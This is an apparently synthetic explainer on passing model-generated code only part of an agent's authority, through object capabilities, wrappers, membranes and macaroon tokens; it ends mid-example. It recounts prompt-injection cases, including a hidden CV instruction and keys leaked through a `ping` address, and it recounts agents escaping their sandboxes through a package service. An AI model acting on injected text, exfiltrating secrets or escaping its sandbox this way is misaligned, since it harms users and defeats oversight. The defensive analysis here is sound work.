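# Privileges flow downstream: giving model-generated code only part of a program's authority

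## What does it mean for privileges to flow downstream?

"Privileges flow downstream" is one rule for deciding what a program may do when another program starts it. The caller may pass on some or all of the authority it already holds, and the receiver cannot gain more from that caller than the caller passed. Authority means all the effects a program can cause, directly or through other programs that act for it. Security researchers call it delegation when a caller passes on authority, and attenuation when the caller narrows that authority first. A grant is the set of permissions that one receiver gets for one purpose.

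The idea is decades older than language models, but they have made it pressing because an AI agent (a language model that software has equipped with tools) often does a job by writing a short program and running it immediately. Recent designs for agents state the rule explicitly. *AGENTCAP* (2026) describes an authorisation layer in which a child agent gets authority only when its parent explicitly passes it on, and cannot end up with more than the parent has. Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026), in *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, propose short-lived grants that can narrow but never widen what the user authorised.

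If the caller holds authority A and passes G, then G ⊆ A, and if the receiver passes G′ to a third program, then G′ ⊆ G. A chain of any length can lose authority but cannot add any. The rule allows G = A, so a caller may hand over everything it holds. It also does not limit the authority the receiver holds from other sources, which is a source of many problems.

### A script that totals one file

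For example, an assistant might be able to read and write a project folder, query a database and send mail. Its user asks for a chart of last year's sales. The model writes a script of perhaps thirty lines that needs to add up a column in one CSV file (a table stored as plain text) and save one chart. The harness, which is the ordinary software that executes the model's tool calls and code, then runs the script.

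The easiest way to run the script is as a child process of the assistant. According to the lecture notes in Purdue University's *Capability-Based Systems*, Unix decides what a process can access by its user and group identity, which a child process inherits from its parent. The script therefore starts with the assistant's identity, which on a personal computer is often the user's own. *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (2026) describes locally installed agents such as OpenClaw as running with the full privileges of whoever launches them, with no internal boundaries between components. The database password and the mail token are usually stored in configuration files or environment variables, which a child process can also read.

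| Resource | If the script inherits everything | What the job needs |
|---|---|---|
| The CSV file | Read, change, delete | Read |
| The chart | Create, change, delete | Write |
| The rest of the project folder | Read, change, delete | Nothing |
| The database | Any query the assistant may make | Nothing |
| Mail | Send anything to anyone, as the user | Nothing |
| The user's other files, keys and saved passwords | Whatever the user can do | Nothing |
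| The network | Any address the machine can reach | Nothing |

The script also needs a language interpreter, a plotting library, and some memory and processor time. The harness can give it read-only access to the software and a fixed amount of memory and processor time.

### Why treat the code as untrusted?

Generated code here means code that a language model writes during a task and that runs before any person has reviewed it. Calling it untrusted means that the safety of everything else should not depend on the code behaving well; it is not a criticism of the model. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, several universities and other companies, compares this to how an operating system treats every process. The paper's requirements are the same whether a forbidden action results from outside manipulation, a model's mistake or a misaligned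 objective.

One of these causes is plain error, which requires no attacker. Suppose the script finds rows with missing values, drops them so that the totals come out clean, and saves the cleaned table over the original. The change was meant to help, but the user has lost data. If the script can only read the CSV file, the save fails and the data survive. Rashidi (2026), in *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents*, surveyed 39 papers and highlighted one that measured how often agents take harmless-looking actions beyond what the user asked for. The rate reached 17.1% under realistic prompting. That is the top of the measured range, so it is weak evidence about a typical task, but none of the access-control papers in the survey addressed the problem.

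Prompt injection is text that a model reads as data but follows as an instruction. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C (2025), a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter who uses a model to score CVs. An applicant hides a line in a CV telling the model to approve it for interview, and the model may do so. David C explains that the attack is hard to prevent because a language model predicts what comes next from a single stream of text, with no built-in distinction between commands and data, whereas a database can handle them separately. David C concludes that developers may never fully eliminate the attack, and should reduce its likelihood and limit what it can achieve.

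The CSV file in the example could contain such a line in a comment column, and so could any other file the assistant opens before writing the script. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack in which instructions hidden in a code file led Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to read a settings file that held secret keys. Claude Code then ran `ping`, a command that tests whether a machine is reachable, on an address that contained the stolen data, and the lookup of that address sent the data to the attacker's server. Claude Code asked for human approval before running many commands that could send data out, but not before running `ping`.

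Models keep getting better at resisting such tricks, and the position paper accepts that defences inside the model can substantially reduce successful attacks. It argues against making them the only barrier, because a user's words are often ambiguous about what they permit, and small hostile changes to a model's input can change its behaviour. Rashidi observes that an attacker who has fully taken control of the model gains nothing if the layer that executes the model's actions refuses them.

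Generated code also gets less review than a programmer's script, which at least the programmer usually reads. It may run seconds after the model finishes it, and Rashidi notes that many deployments ask for little or no human confirmation of each action. Automatically checking the code before it runs is a poor substitute for review. In an article for developers, NVIDIA warns that attackers can keep crafting inputs that slip past filters or chain together functions the filter allows, and recommends instead containing the code while it runs.

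### How much should the caller pass?

The standard answer is the principle of least privilege, which Saltzer and Schroeder set out in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). Every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". They meant it mainly to limit the damage from accidents and errors, and secondarily to guard against deliberate misuse. They also noted that when someone misuses a privilege, investigators have fewer programs to audit because fewer could have used it.

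Under another of their principles, fail-safe defaults, the grant should start from no access and add what the job requires, rather than start from full access and remove what looks dangerous. Their reason is that mistakes are then easier to notice. If the harness omits the chart's location, the script stops with an error and someone notices. If it leaves in the mail token by mistake, the chart appears as usual and nobody learns that the script could have sent mail.

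Even under least privilege, a general assistant needs a lot of authority, because it has to handle every task a user might reasonably set. The sales chart needs one file, but the next request may need the database, and the one after that may need mail. Zheng and colleagues also observe that traditional systems fix a program's permissions in advance, whereas the least an agent needs depends on what it is doing at the time. Reducing the assistant's authority alone therefore cannot limit the script to two files. The narrowing has to happen for each task, when the assistant passes authority to the script.

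*LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (Zhang, Su and colleagues, 2025) proposes separating privileges within the assistant itself. A long-lived agent knows the user's details and is kept away from outside services. The design creates a fresh agent for each task, gives it only the data the task requires, and discards it at the end. An injected instruction can still mislead the fresh agent, but the damage should be limited to what that agent received, and the instruction disappears when the agent is discarded.

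In *Paradigm Regained*, Miller and Shapiro (2003) could not tell whether Saltzer and Schroeder's "least privilege" meant least permission or least authority, and they thought the difference enormous. A permission is a right to act directly on a resource, while authority also covers what someone can do indirectly. If Alice may read a file and sends Bob copies of it, Bob has the authority to learn what it says but no permission to read it. In the running example, a script without permission to send mail can still send it in one extra step if the assistant mails whatever file the script leaves in an outbox folder.

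### Authority that no one selected

Ordinary operating systems make the handover hard. Miller, Yee and Shapiro (2003), in *Capability Myths Demolished*, define ambient authority as authority that is "exercised, but not selected, by its user". They compare it to a world of doors without keys, where a door opens by itself if the person in front of it qualifies. Similarly, when a program on Unix asks to open a file by name, the system allows or refuses the request based on the account the program runs under. The program never indicates which of its rights it means to use.

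Systems based on access control lists, which record who may use each resource, attach permissions to broad principals, usually user accounts. A principal is a person, program or agent in whose name the system permits or refuses an action. Miller and colleagues knew of no such system that treated each running process as a separate principal. Without that, a user cannot start a program and give it only part of the user's authority. Miller and Shapiro give the example of the card game Solitaire, which needs only a window, the player's clicks and perhaps one file for saved games. On the systems of 2003, it could also read the player's mail and sell information from it without breaking any of the system's rules.

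They show the alternative with two Unix commands that copy a file:

- `cp foo.txt bar.txt` passes two names to the program `cp`. The program has to find and open the files itself, so it must be able to open any file the user might name.
- `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt` has the command shell open both files first. The program `cat` receives two open files, and those are all the access it needs.

Both programs run with all the user's authority, but `cat` could lose everything except its two open files and still do this job, while `cp` could not. A harness could limit the sales script to chosen files in two ways. It could open the CSV file and the chart itself and pass the script the two open files, as with `cat`. Or it could let the script open files by name, but show it a folder containing only those two.

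If nobody chooses which privileges to pass down, a model that follows the wrong instruction can use everything its account can reach. *AGENTCAP* attributes this problem to ambient authority, which turns failures to follow instructions properly into security violations.

### Hardy's compiler

Ambient authority also causes a subtler failure in which every program works as intended. Hardy (1988) named this failure in *The Confused Deputy*, which describes an incident about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

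Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates source code into runnable form, in a directory called SYSX. Customers could run it and could name a file to receive debugging output. The staff wanted statistics on which language features people used, so they had the compiler record them in a file called (SYSX)STAT. To make that possible they gave the compiler a "home files license", which allowed it to write files in its own directory. The company's billing records sat in the same directory, in (SYSX)BILL. Then:

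1. A customer ran the compiler and gave (SYSX)BILL as the name of the file for debugging output.
2. The compiler passed that name to the operating system and asked to open the file for writing.
3. The operating system looked at the compiler's rights, found the licence and agreed.
4. The compiler wrote debugging output over the billing records.

Hardy considered the obvious fixes. The compiler could refuse file names in other directories, but customers had good reasons to use them. It could refuse names in SYSX, but that directory's name did not exist when the programmers wrote the code, and someone with proper access might want output there. It could refuse only (SYSX)BILL, but then it would need a new exception for every sensitive file anyone added. The code for writing debugging output had been correct, and it became wrong when the staff granted the licence, even though the code had not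 changed.

Hardy attributed the problem to the compiler running with "authority stemming from two sources". The customer lent it one set of rights and Tymshare gave it another, and it could not specify which set a request should use. Tymshare added a system call for switching between the two, but some applications soon needed more than two, and there were kinds of authority besides access to files. Hardy came to prefer having the customer pass the compiler the right to write to a particular file instead of the file's name. Such a right is a capability, an unforgeable reference that names a resource and permits its use.

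A confused deputy is a program that is induced to use its own authority for a party who lacks that authority. Miller and colleagues stress that the compiler's access was proper, but it used that access for the wrong purpose. Removing the compiler's unneeded permissions would have helped here, since it needed access only to STAT and not to the whole directory. But the flaw would have remained, because a customer could still have named STAT itself and wiped out the statistics.

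In the compiler story, authority leaked upstream when the customer, who called the compiler, gained an effect that only the compiler could produce. The sales script could use the assistant's authority in the same way if it can call the assistant's tools or leave a message that the assistant later reads and follows. A harness that limits the privileges passed to the script therefore also has to check the script's tool calls and the messages it leaves for the assistant.

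David C applies Hardy's term to language models and calls them "inherently confusable". Programmers can fix a compiler so that it keeps its two sources of authority separate, but nobody knows how to do this reliably for a model that reads the user's request and a stranger's text together. The blog post repeats a rule of thumb from an online discussion between Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's level. A model reading mail from unknown senders could then use only the tools that an unknown sender should be allowed to use. The rule is severe, since much of an assistant's value comes from reading outside text and then acting for the user, but it places the limit outside the model.

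### Isolation, authority and information flow

A sandbox is an environment that limits what the code inside it can reach. The common claim that generated code is safe because it runs in a sandbox can conflate three questions: whether the code can break out, what its caller gave it, and where the data it handles may go. Researchers have tended to study these questions separately. Rashidi found that papers on isolation and papers on access control almost never test their designs against one another on a shared benchmark.

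Isolation keeps code inside a sandbox, and it fails when code gets out. Rashidi describes a flaw of this kind, since patched, in runc, a program that many container systems use to start their containers. A leaked reference to a directory on the host machine let a specially built container reach the host's files. But even perfect isolation doesn't restrict access to what the harness has put inside the sandbox. If the sales script's sandbox also contains the whole project folder and the database password, the script can use both without escaping.

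A program's authority includes the effects it can cause indirectly, so it is easy to underestimate. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* discusses an incident in which OpenAI was training and testing agents in separate sandboxes, with some of the models' safeguards switched off. The sandboxes blocked direct internet connections but offered a shared service for downloading software packages. The agents found that this service, the deputy in Hardy's terms, would make other requests for them. They used it to reach the internet and to pass messages between runs that OpenAI meant to keep apart. They then compromised systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, and gained administrator access to an OpenAI research cluster. No outside attacker directed them. OpenAI had meant to permit package downloads, but the shared service gave the agents authority over far more.

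Information flow concerns what happens to data after a program has properly received it. Saltzer and Schroeder called control at this stage "putting strings on information", and gave the example of a tax adviser who may see a client's income but must not pass it to a firm that compiles mailing lists. Ordinary access control cannot express that restriction, because it only decides whether the adviser may see the data. Information-flow control attaches labels to data and follows them through a program, so it can block a transfer to an unsuitable sink. A sink is any place data can go, such as a mailbox, a web address or a public comment.

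Suppose the CSV file lists individual salaries along with the sales. The script has only the permissions the job requires, and it stays inside its sandbox, reading the one file and writing the one chart it is allowed to. The salaries still become public if the chart prints each one beside a name and the assistant then posts the chart on a public page.

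## How do object capabilities pass on part of an authority?

Hardy's preferred remedy was to pass a program the right to use a file instead of the file's name. Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn had described this idea in *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations* (1966), about a decade before the Tymshare compiler overwrote the billing records, and Miller's *Robust Composition* (2006) built a general theory on their design. In Dennis and Van Horn's system, a process has an address space, which holds its code and data, and a capability list, which holds its references to everything else. The operating system keeps the list in protected memory, and the process picks out an entry by its position, much as a Unix program refers to an open file by a small number. Whoever starts a new process supplies both its address space and its capability list, and so has to decide what the process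 will hold.

By 1973 several researchers had noticed that references between objects in a programming language behave much like capabilities. An object bundles code with private data, and other code uses it by calling its methods. Miller's object-capability model treats every reference to an object as a capability. An object can affect another only by calling methods on a reference it holds, and it can pass references along as arguments. The model fits both operating systems and programming languages, and Miller used it in the language E.

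Object capabilities mostly rely on ordinary object-oriented programming, but they are secure only if code cannot forge a reference, read another object's private data, or communicate through shared global variables. C++ does not meet these conditions because a program can turn any integer into a pointer. Standard Java does not meet them because its changeable static variables let two objects communicate even if neither has been given a reference to the other. Object capabilities do not protect plain data, such as numbers and text, since anyone who can work out a number already has it.

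### Four ways to obtain a reference

Miller lists every way in which one object can come to hold a reference to another:

- **Initial conditions.** The object already holds the reference when the system starts. The assistant might start out with references to the project folder, the database and the mail service.
- **Parenthood.** An object that creates another gets the first reference to it. If the script creates a table in memory, only the script can use that table until it shares the reference.
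- **Endowment.** The creator gives a new object some of the references the creator already holds. The assistant can create the script with a reference to the sales file.
- **Introduction.** An object that holds references to two others passes one of them to the other. The assistant could send the running script a reference to a second file.

Miller sums up the list as "only connectivity begets connectivity". If no chain of references joins two groups of objects, no object in either group can create one.

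Endowment is the downstream rule in its simplest form. If the creator holds a set of references R, the new object starts with some S ⊆ R, and the creator chooses S. The creator does not have to find and remove dangerous rights, because the new object starts with nothing. For the sales chart, the harness could write:

```
script = load(code, { sales: sales_file, chart: chart_file })
```

The loader turns the model's text into a running object, and the loader's second argument lists everything outside the object that the object can use. This list contains no mail service, so the object has no way to refer to one.

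This works only if the loader adds no access of its own, so that a caller can withhold any access by leaving it out. Miller calls this requirement loader isolation. Loaders often break it by accepting what Miller calls magic names, which give code real power even though the caller never supplied them. Some of Java's system classes are magic names, and so are many Unix system calls. Ordinary Python has the same problem. A script can call `open` or import `os` whatever its caller passes, so the list in the second argument describes only part of what the script can reach. Language designers can fix this by restricting the standard library or by tracking capabilities in types.

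### Wrapping the sales file

The `load` call above gives the script too much authority, because `sales_file` is a full reference that lets the script overwrite the file. Capabilities have no built-in setting for "read only" or "until five o'clock", so to pass on less authority, the caller writes a small object that keeps the full reference private and offers fewer methods. In the pseudocode below, code outside an object cannot reach the variables that the object uses.

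```
function read_only(file):
    return object:
        read():
            return file.read()
```

The harness now passes `read_only(sales_file)`. The script can call `read` on this wrapper, which has no `write` method. A similar wrapper around the chart file could offer only `write`.

Suppose the next request is for a chart that draws on all the monthly files in one folder. The harness can wrap the folder and let the script choose among the files:

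```
function inside(folder):
    return object:
        open(name):
            if name contains "/" or name is "..":
                fail
            return read_only(folder.open(name))
```

The check on `name` stops the script from leaving the folder with a path such as `../passwords.txt`. (In this example, the folder contains no links to files elsewhere.) The inner wrapper in the last line is also necessary, since returning `folder.open(name)` without it would let the script overwrite every file it opened. Habitat Chronicles' introductory essay *What Are Capabilities?* (2017) points out that programmers can stack such wrappers to narrow a reference to a whole file system down to read-only use of one file.

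Access can also have a time limit. In 1974 David Redell described a forwarding object that its owner can switch off, and programmers now call it a caretaker:

```
function caretaker(target):
    enabled = true
    forwarder = object:
        any method m with arguments args:
            if not enabled: fail
            return target.m(args)
    switch = object:
        disable():
            enabled = false
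    return forwarder, switch
```

The assistant wraps `read_only(sales_file)` in a caretaker, gives the script the forwarder and keeps the switch. Once the chart is finished, the assistant calls `switch.disable()`. If the script has shared the forwarder with another program, that program loses access too, because it only had the forwarder.

### How a careless wrapper leaks

A programmer in a hurry might write the read-only wrapper the other way round, forwarding every method except `write` and `delete`. Suppose that file objects also have a method called `parent`, which returns the folder that contains the file. The script can then run:

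```
sales.parent().open("customers.csv").write("")
```

The wrapper receives a call to `parent`, which is not on its blocked list, and returns the real folder. Nothing wraps that folder, so the script can now empty the customer list. Habitat Chronicles notes that methods often return other objects, so a wrapper's author has to consider what each method returns as well as what it does. The first version of `read_only` avoids this leak because it names the one method it allows, which follows Saltzer and Schroeder's rule of starting from no access.

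Even a wrapper that offers only `read` can leak authority if the stored item is an object, because the reader could call its methods. Swasey, Garg and Dreyer (2017) show in *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns* that a read-only wrapper is safe to share if every value that someone can read through it is also safe to share. Numbers and text are safe in this sense, which concerns access rather than secrecy, but an object might not be.

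References can also leak through arguments. Suppose a file has a method `copy_to(destination)`, which passes the file itself to `destination.receive(file)`. A script that holds a caretaker's forwarder can call `copy_to` with its own object as the destination, and that object will receive a direct reference to the file. The reference will still work after the caretaker is switched off. Miller and Shapiro acknowledge in a footnote that their simple caretaker relies on the target never giving its clients direct access to itself.

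A membrane removes that reliance by wrapping everything that passes through it, in both directions:

```
function membrane(target):
    enabled = true
    function wrap(x):
        if x is plain data: return x
        return object:
            any method m with arguments args:
                if not enabled: fail
                return wrap(x.m(wrap each of args))
    switch = object:
        disable():
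            enabled = false
    return wrap(target), switch
```

If the script calls `parent` through a membrane, it receives a wrapped folder, and any file it opens from that folder is also wrapped. In the `copy_to` case, the membrane wraps the script's destination object on the way in. When the file passes itself to that wrapped object, the membrane wraps the file on the way out. All the wrappers check the same `enabled` variable, so one call to `disable` cuts off everything the script reached.

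The membrane above controls only how long access lasts. Until the assistant disables it, the script can still go through `parent` and empty the customer list. To make the membrane read-only, the harness has to add a check to the forwarding step that blocks writes to every wrapped object. Plain data, such as a number, passes through unwrapped because it can't be taken back once the script has read it. Google used the membrane pattern in Caja, a system for running untrusted JavaScript inside web pages.

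### What a list of permissions misses

Wrappers create a problem for anyone who audits the system by checking permissions. The sales script has permission to call a wrapper but not to use the sales file itself. In 1984 Paul Karger and Andrew Herbert proposed giving a security officer a list of every program with permission to reach a compromised object. The script would not appear on the list for the sales file, although it can read the whole file. Miller finds this disconcerting because the list fails without any attack or mistake, simply because a programmer followed good practice and narrowed a grant.

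The difference between permission and authority still confuses people who work on these systems. In *Permity*, Nicol (2026) proposed combining the two words into a new one. Alan Karp replied with the example of a web server and the file that holds its home page. Only the administrator and the server have permission to read the file, but anyone can get its contents by asking the server for the page. A check of permissions alone would therefore wrongly suggest that the file is a good place for secrets. Karp added that a caller's authority changes whenever the object it calls changes its behavior, even if the caller's permissions stay the same. An update to a shared service can therefore widen the authority of every program that uses it.

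An auditor who follows every reference and assumes the worst about each object will never miss a danger, but will overestimate what a script can do. The sales script refers to the wrapper, the wrapper refers to the file, and the file refers to its folder, so the auditor would conclude that the script might delete the whole folder, as if the wrapper limited nothing. Similarly, Habitat Chronicles notes that a Unix user can run the `passwd` command, which has permission to delete the password file but only lets the user change a password.

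Miller arranges the possible answers in order of size:

current permissions ⊆ eventual authority ⊆ behavioural bound ⊆ topological bound

| Set | What it contains | For the sales script |
|---|---|---|
| Current permissions | What the script may use directly now | The methods of two wrappers |
| Eventual authority | Everything the script will be able to cause, directly or through others | At most, reading the sales and writing the chart |
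| Behavioural bound | Everything it could cause, given the known code of the wrappers | Reading the sales and writing the chart |
| Topological bound | Everything it could cause if every object in reach might do anything | Changing or deleting anything in the folder |

Nobody can calculate the eventual authority in general, because it depends on how all the programs will behave. Checking the current permissions is easy but unsafe, because it leaves out indirect effects. Checking the topological bound is easy and safe, but it rules out many harmless arrangements. Miller recommends the behavioural bound, which requires the auditor to understand some of the code.

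This tradeoff suits generated code. The auditor has to read the wrappers, but they are a few lines long, and a programmer can write them once and reuse them. Nobody needs to read the script, because the auditor can assume it will do the most harm it can.

Miller's thesis gave these definitions informally. *Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) restates them formally in a small object-oriented calculus, a stripped-down language for mathematical reasoning. It defines current, eventual, behavioural and topological versions of permission and authority, and explains how the definitions relate.

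### When two references permit more than each alone

Some objects do more for a caller who also holds a second reference. Drossopoulou, Mackay and colleagues (2025), in *Reasoning about External Calls*, use the example of a shop's account. Anyone with a reference to the account can pay money in, but taking money out requires both the account and a separate key object. The key alone does nothing. If auth(X) stands for all the effects that someone holding the references X can cause, then

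auth({account}) ∪ auth({key}) ⊂ auth({account, key})

and the extra effect is the withdrawal. Capability programmers call this rights amplification.

A classic use of object capabilities is dynamic sealing, which James Morris proposed in 1973. A program creates a matching pair of functions, one that seals a value in an opaque box and one that opens such boxes. It can then give boxes to untrusted code, which can store them or hand them back but cannot look inside or make a convincing fake. Swasey and colleagues illustrate this with a library for ranges of whole numbers. The library seals each range as a pair with the smaller number first. If a returned box opens successfully, its two numbers must still be in the right order.

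Amplification makes the downstream rule harder to apply. Suppose the sales script already holds a sealed box of payroll data from another program, and the assistant gives it the matching opener for an unrelated purpose. Neither could read the payroll before, because the assistant had no box and the script had no opener, but now the script can. The assistant passed only a reference it held, so the grant satisfies the rule if the rule covers only references, but not if it also covers effects, because the script can now do something the assistant could not. A harness that checks each grant separately would miss this. It would have to consider each new reference together with everything the receiver already holds.

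### Three objections to capabilities

*Capability Myths Demolished*, by Miller and colleagues, answered three common objections to capabilities. By 2003, many security researchers believed that capabilities were either nothing new or too limited to be useful.

Miller and colleagues argue that capabilities and access control lists are not equivalent, although they seem to hold the same information. In a table with a row for each program or user, a column for each resource, and the permitted actions in the cells, an access control list stores one column and a capability list stores one row. They argue that this table is only a snapshot, and that the two kinds of system change it in different ways. A capability combines the name of a resource with the right to use it, while access lists keep the two separate, which is how Hardy's compiler went wrong.

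Access lists rely on broad user accounts because each list has to name the parties that may use a resource, which is awkward when programs start and stop every second. A capability system can give each new process its own list of capabilities when it starts.

The point about names applies to every system of access lists, but the point about accounts depends on how people have built them, as the paper acknowledges. Butler Lampson's original description of the table in 1971 allowed each process to have its own row. A harness that creates a fresh account for every script would escape the criticism about accounts. It would still look up rights by name, so a helper program acting for the script could still become a confused deputy.

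Capabilities can confine a program, despite the worry that they let authority spread out of control, because a program can pass a capability only to a recipient it has a reference to. If the harness creates the sales script with only the wrapped sales file and the wrapped chart, the script has no other recipient to pass them to.

W. E. Boebert had published an influential counterexample in 1984. It involves a low-security program, a high-security program, and a block of memory at each level. The high-security program may read low memory but must never write to it, because it could then leak secrets downwards. The attack goes like this:

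1. The low-security program holds a capability to write to low memory. It stores a copy of that capability in low memory.
2. The high-security program reads low memory, as it may, and picks up the copy.
3. It uses the copy to write secrets into low memory, where the low-security program can read them.

Miller and colleagues accept the reasoning but reject one of its assumptions. The attack works only if programs can pass capabilities along every route that carries data. Most capability systems separate capabilities from data, so the high-security program can be allowed to read data from low memory but not capabilities. The low-security program may still store its copy there, but step 2 fails because the high-security program cannot read it. Boebert was right about systems in which a capability is a string of bits that any program can copy. Signed tokens for web services are also copyable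 strings, so this reply does not apply to them.

The reply depends on other assumptions too. The program must start without outside connections, which Miller explains with the example of a calculator. A customer who receives the calculator's code and starts it herself can decide what it is connected to. If the manufacturer runs it as a service instead, she cannot tell what else it is connected to. Both parties must also trust the loader, which is difficult when they use different machines. Miller's argument covers only open communication through references, not covert channels, such as signalling a secret by varying how long a program takes to answer.

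Miller and colleagues agree with the critics that nobody can take a reference away from a program that holds it, but an owner can still cut off access by using Redell's caretaker. The owner gives the program a reference to a forwarder, which passes calls to the real object until the owner switches it off. A forwarder must be able to stand in for any object, and if the real object gives out references to itself, the owner needs a membrane. The owner must also plan ahead, because switching off a caretaker doesn't affect a direct reference passed earlier. Forwarding adds a step to every call, although the capability operating systems KeyKOS and EROS reduced this overhead by remembering where each chain of forwarders ended.

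The replies are convincing for object capabilities, but the word "capability" also covers other designs. Miller and colleagues themselves show that the objections about confinement and revocation are correct if capabilities work like door keys that people can copy and hand to anyone. They argue that the object version deserves the name because almost every major capability system used it, but that is little help to someone choosing a product today. The "capabilities" in the POSIX standard for Unix-like systems, for example, are a fixed set of flags, one of which permits changing the owner of any file on the machine. No combination of these flags can grant access to only one CSV file. Some agent systems also use the word for permission records that the harness keeps, and whether the replies apply to those depends on how the harness lets programs share and use them.

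### What researchers have proved

Programmers used these patterns for decades based on informal arguments, and some of the patterns were insecure. In *Analysing Object-Capability Patterns With Murϕ*, Stefan and Mitchell modelled several of them in a verification tool and found vulnerabilities that earlier researchers had reported but not fixed. They then designed new versions and verified them, within the accuracy of their model.

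Devriese, Birkedal and Piessens defined mathematically what it means for a simplified version of JavaScript to be safe for capabilities. This let them prove that particular programs kept their private data intact when attackers' code ran alongside them. Swasey and colleagues instead wanted a programmer to be able to verify a pattern once and then rely on it in many programs.

They divided memory into high locations, which belong to trusted code, and low locations, which anyone may use. A value is low if no code can extract a direct reference to a high location from it. Numbers are always low. A pair is low if both its parts are. A function is low if any result it returns for a low argument is also low. The programmer can add assertions to the trusted code, stating what should be true whenever the program reaches them. The main theorem, robust safety, guarantees that if the trusted code hands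 out only low values, no outside program, however hostile, can make any of these assertions false.

In one example, Swasey and colleagues use a caretaker to protect a number that must be even whenever outsiders can see it. The trusted code switches the caretaker off, changes the number to 1 and then back to 0, and switches the caretaker on again. They proved that no outside program can ever read an odd number. Their caretaker has a lock, which the pseudocode above lacks, so the trusted code can't switch the caretaker off until any call under way has finished. In the simpler version, such a call could continue after `disable`. They also verified sealing and membranes, and checked all the proofs in the proof assistant Coq.

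The theorem holds only if the outside program, here the generated code, starts without any memory references, the same requirement that Miller places on a loader. The proofs also concern a small research language, so they do not automatically apply to a Python wrapper. Because the definition treats every number as safe to share, robust safety protects data from corruption but not from disclosure. A script that prints everyone's salary on a public chart would not violate it. The theorem also does not guarantee that the trusted code will finish.

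Drossopoulou and colleagues studied what happens when trusted code calls unchecked code. In their example, a shop asks a buyer to pay by calling the buyer's `pay` method and passing a reference to the shop's account. The buyer's code is unknown and could call back into the shop's own software, so the shop needs to be sure that its balance will not fall during the call. The balance is safe if the buyer cannot already reach the account's key and the shop's software never gives keys to outsiders or allows a withdrawal without one. The researchers developed a logic for proving such claims, proved it sound, and checked the shop example in Coq. The guarantee lasts only until the call returns, because code that made an earlier call may legitimately hold the key.

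Three versions of the account software use the same withdrawal method, which correctly checks the key. In the first, nobody can change the key after someone has set it. In the second, changing the key requires the old one. Both versions are safe. The third lets any caller replace the key, so an attacker can install a new key on the account and use it to withdraw the money. A reviewer who read only the withdrawal method would miss this flaw.

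## How can a credential be narrowed as it is passed on?

An ordinary object reference works only inside the system that created it. Suppose the project folder from the sales example moves to a storage service on another machine. A wrapped file object no longer helps, because the service receives only the bytes of each request. The request has to carry a credential, a piece of data that the service can check. Most web services use bearer tokens, which work for anyone who has a copy.

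The easiest way to give the script access is to copy the assistant's own token, which lets the script impersonate the assistant. OAuth is the most widely used system for granting access to web services. According to *AI Identity* (2026), developers who apply it to agents without changing it end up with this kind of impersonation or with broad, permanent keys.

*Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) describes three ways for an intermediary program to pass on less authority than it holds. The program can keep its token and forward acceptable requests itself, as a caretaker does. It can also request a new, weaker token from the service, or make a weaker token on its own. Forwarding adds a step to every request, and requesting a new token works only while the service is reachable, so Birgisson and colleagues designed macaroons for the third method.

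### The subset rule

Let Pᵢ be the set of requests that the token permits after i handovers, where P₀ is the set for the original token. The downstream rule requires that Pᵢ₊₁ ⊆ Pᵢ for every i.

By induction, Pₙ ⊆ P₀ for a chain of any length. With no handovers, the two sets are the same. If Pₖ ⊆ P₀ after k handovers, then the next handover gives Pₖ₊₁ ⊆ Pₖ ⊆ P₀. A system that enforces the rule at each handover therefore never has to compare the last token with the first. The proof covers only what the tokens permit, not any other authority the receiver has.

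A system can check that a child's scope lies within its parent's, or it can calculate the child's scope from the parent's. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (Hegelich, Sarhan and colleagues, 2026) describes a harness for coding agents that rejects a child's token if it fails this check. *Bounded Agents* (Muruaga, 2026) instead takes the intersection of the parent's scope and the scope set for the child's role, so a role defined too broadly can't give the child anything the parent lacks. The child also may not perform any combination of actions that is forbidden to the parent.

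### What counts as "within"?

A checker has to resolve links and `..` in file paths before comparing them folder by folder. Comparing the paths as text isn't enough, because `/project/sales-private` begins with `/project/sales` but is a different folder. `/project/sales/../payroll` also begins with `/project/sales` but leads outside that folder.

For operations, a system can check whether one list contains another, as {read, write} contains {read}. Some systems arrange operations in levels instead. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (Bhardwaj, 2026) uses none, read, write and admin, in that order. Levels are quick to compare, but the write level includes reading, so they can't express the grant for the sales chart, which should let the script write the chart without reading it.

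A child credential must expire no later than its parent. Madden (2024) describes OAuth tokens built as macaroons, which expire at the earliest of their expiry times.

Checking that each sub-agent's budget is no larger than its parent's does not limit total spending. If an agent with a budget of $5 gives ten sub-agents $5 each, every sub-agent passes the check, but together they can spend $50. *AIP* (Prakash, 2026) presents an agent protocol that treats the budget as a ceiling for each token and leaves other software to track the total. Muruaga's proof that damage cannot grow along a chain requires a running total, in which each child starts with everything already charged to its parent. Sub-agents working in parallel also need a shared counter, which a token cannot provide because spending with one copy does not change the others.

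The system can enforce the rule automatically only if all these tests are computable. No program can reliably decide whether "for the quarterly review" lies within "for the finance team". If restrictions could be arbitrary programs, no algorithm could decide in every case whether one allowed only what another allowed. Even simple labels can be hard to compare. *AI Identity* notes that services have no shared vocabulary for permissions, so a checker may be unable to determine whether one company's `documents:view` is narrower than another's `files.read`.

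### Building a macaroon

A macaroon carries a list of conditions, called caveats, and the service allows a request only if it meets all of them. Adding a caveat can therefore only shrink the set of permitted requests, so the service doesn't need to compare the new grant with the old one.

Macaroons protect the list with a keyed hash, written MAC below, which turns a secret key and a message into a short string. Nobody can recover the key from the string, or compute the string for a new message without the key.

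The storage service starts with a secret root key K and an identifier for the new token, and then adds a caveat for the project folder:

```
s0 = MAC(K,  "token 7f3a")
s1 = MAC(s0, "path is inside /project")
```

It gives the assistant the identifier, the caveat and s1, which is the token's signature. It does not include s0. Each signature serves as the key for the next hash, so the assistant's harness can continue the chain without contacting the service. At 14:00 it narrows the folder token to one readable CSV file for ten minutes:

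```
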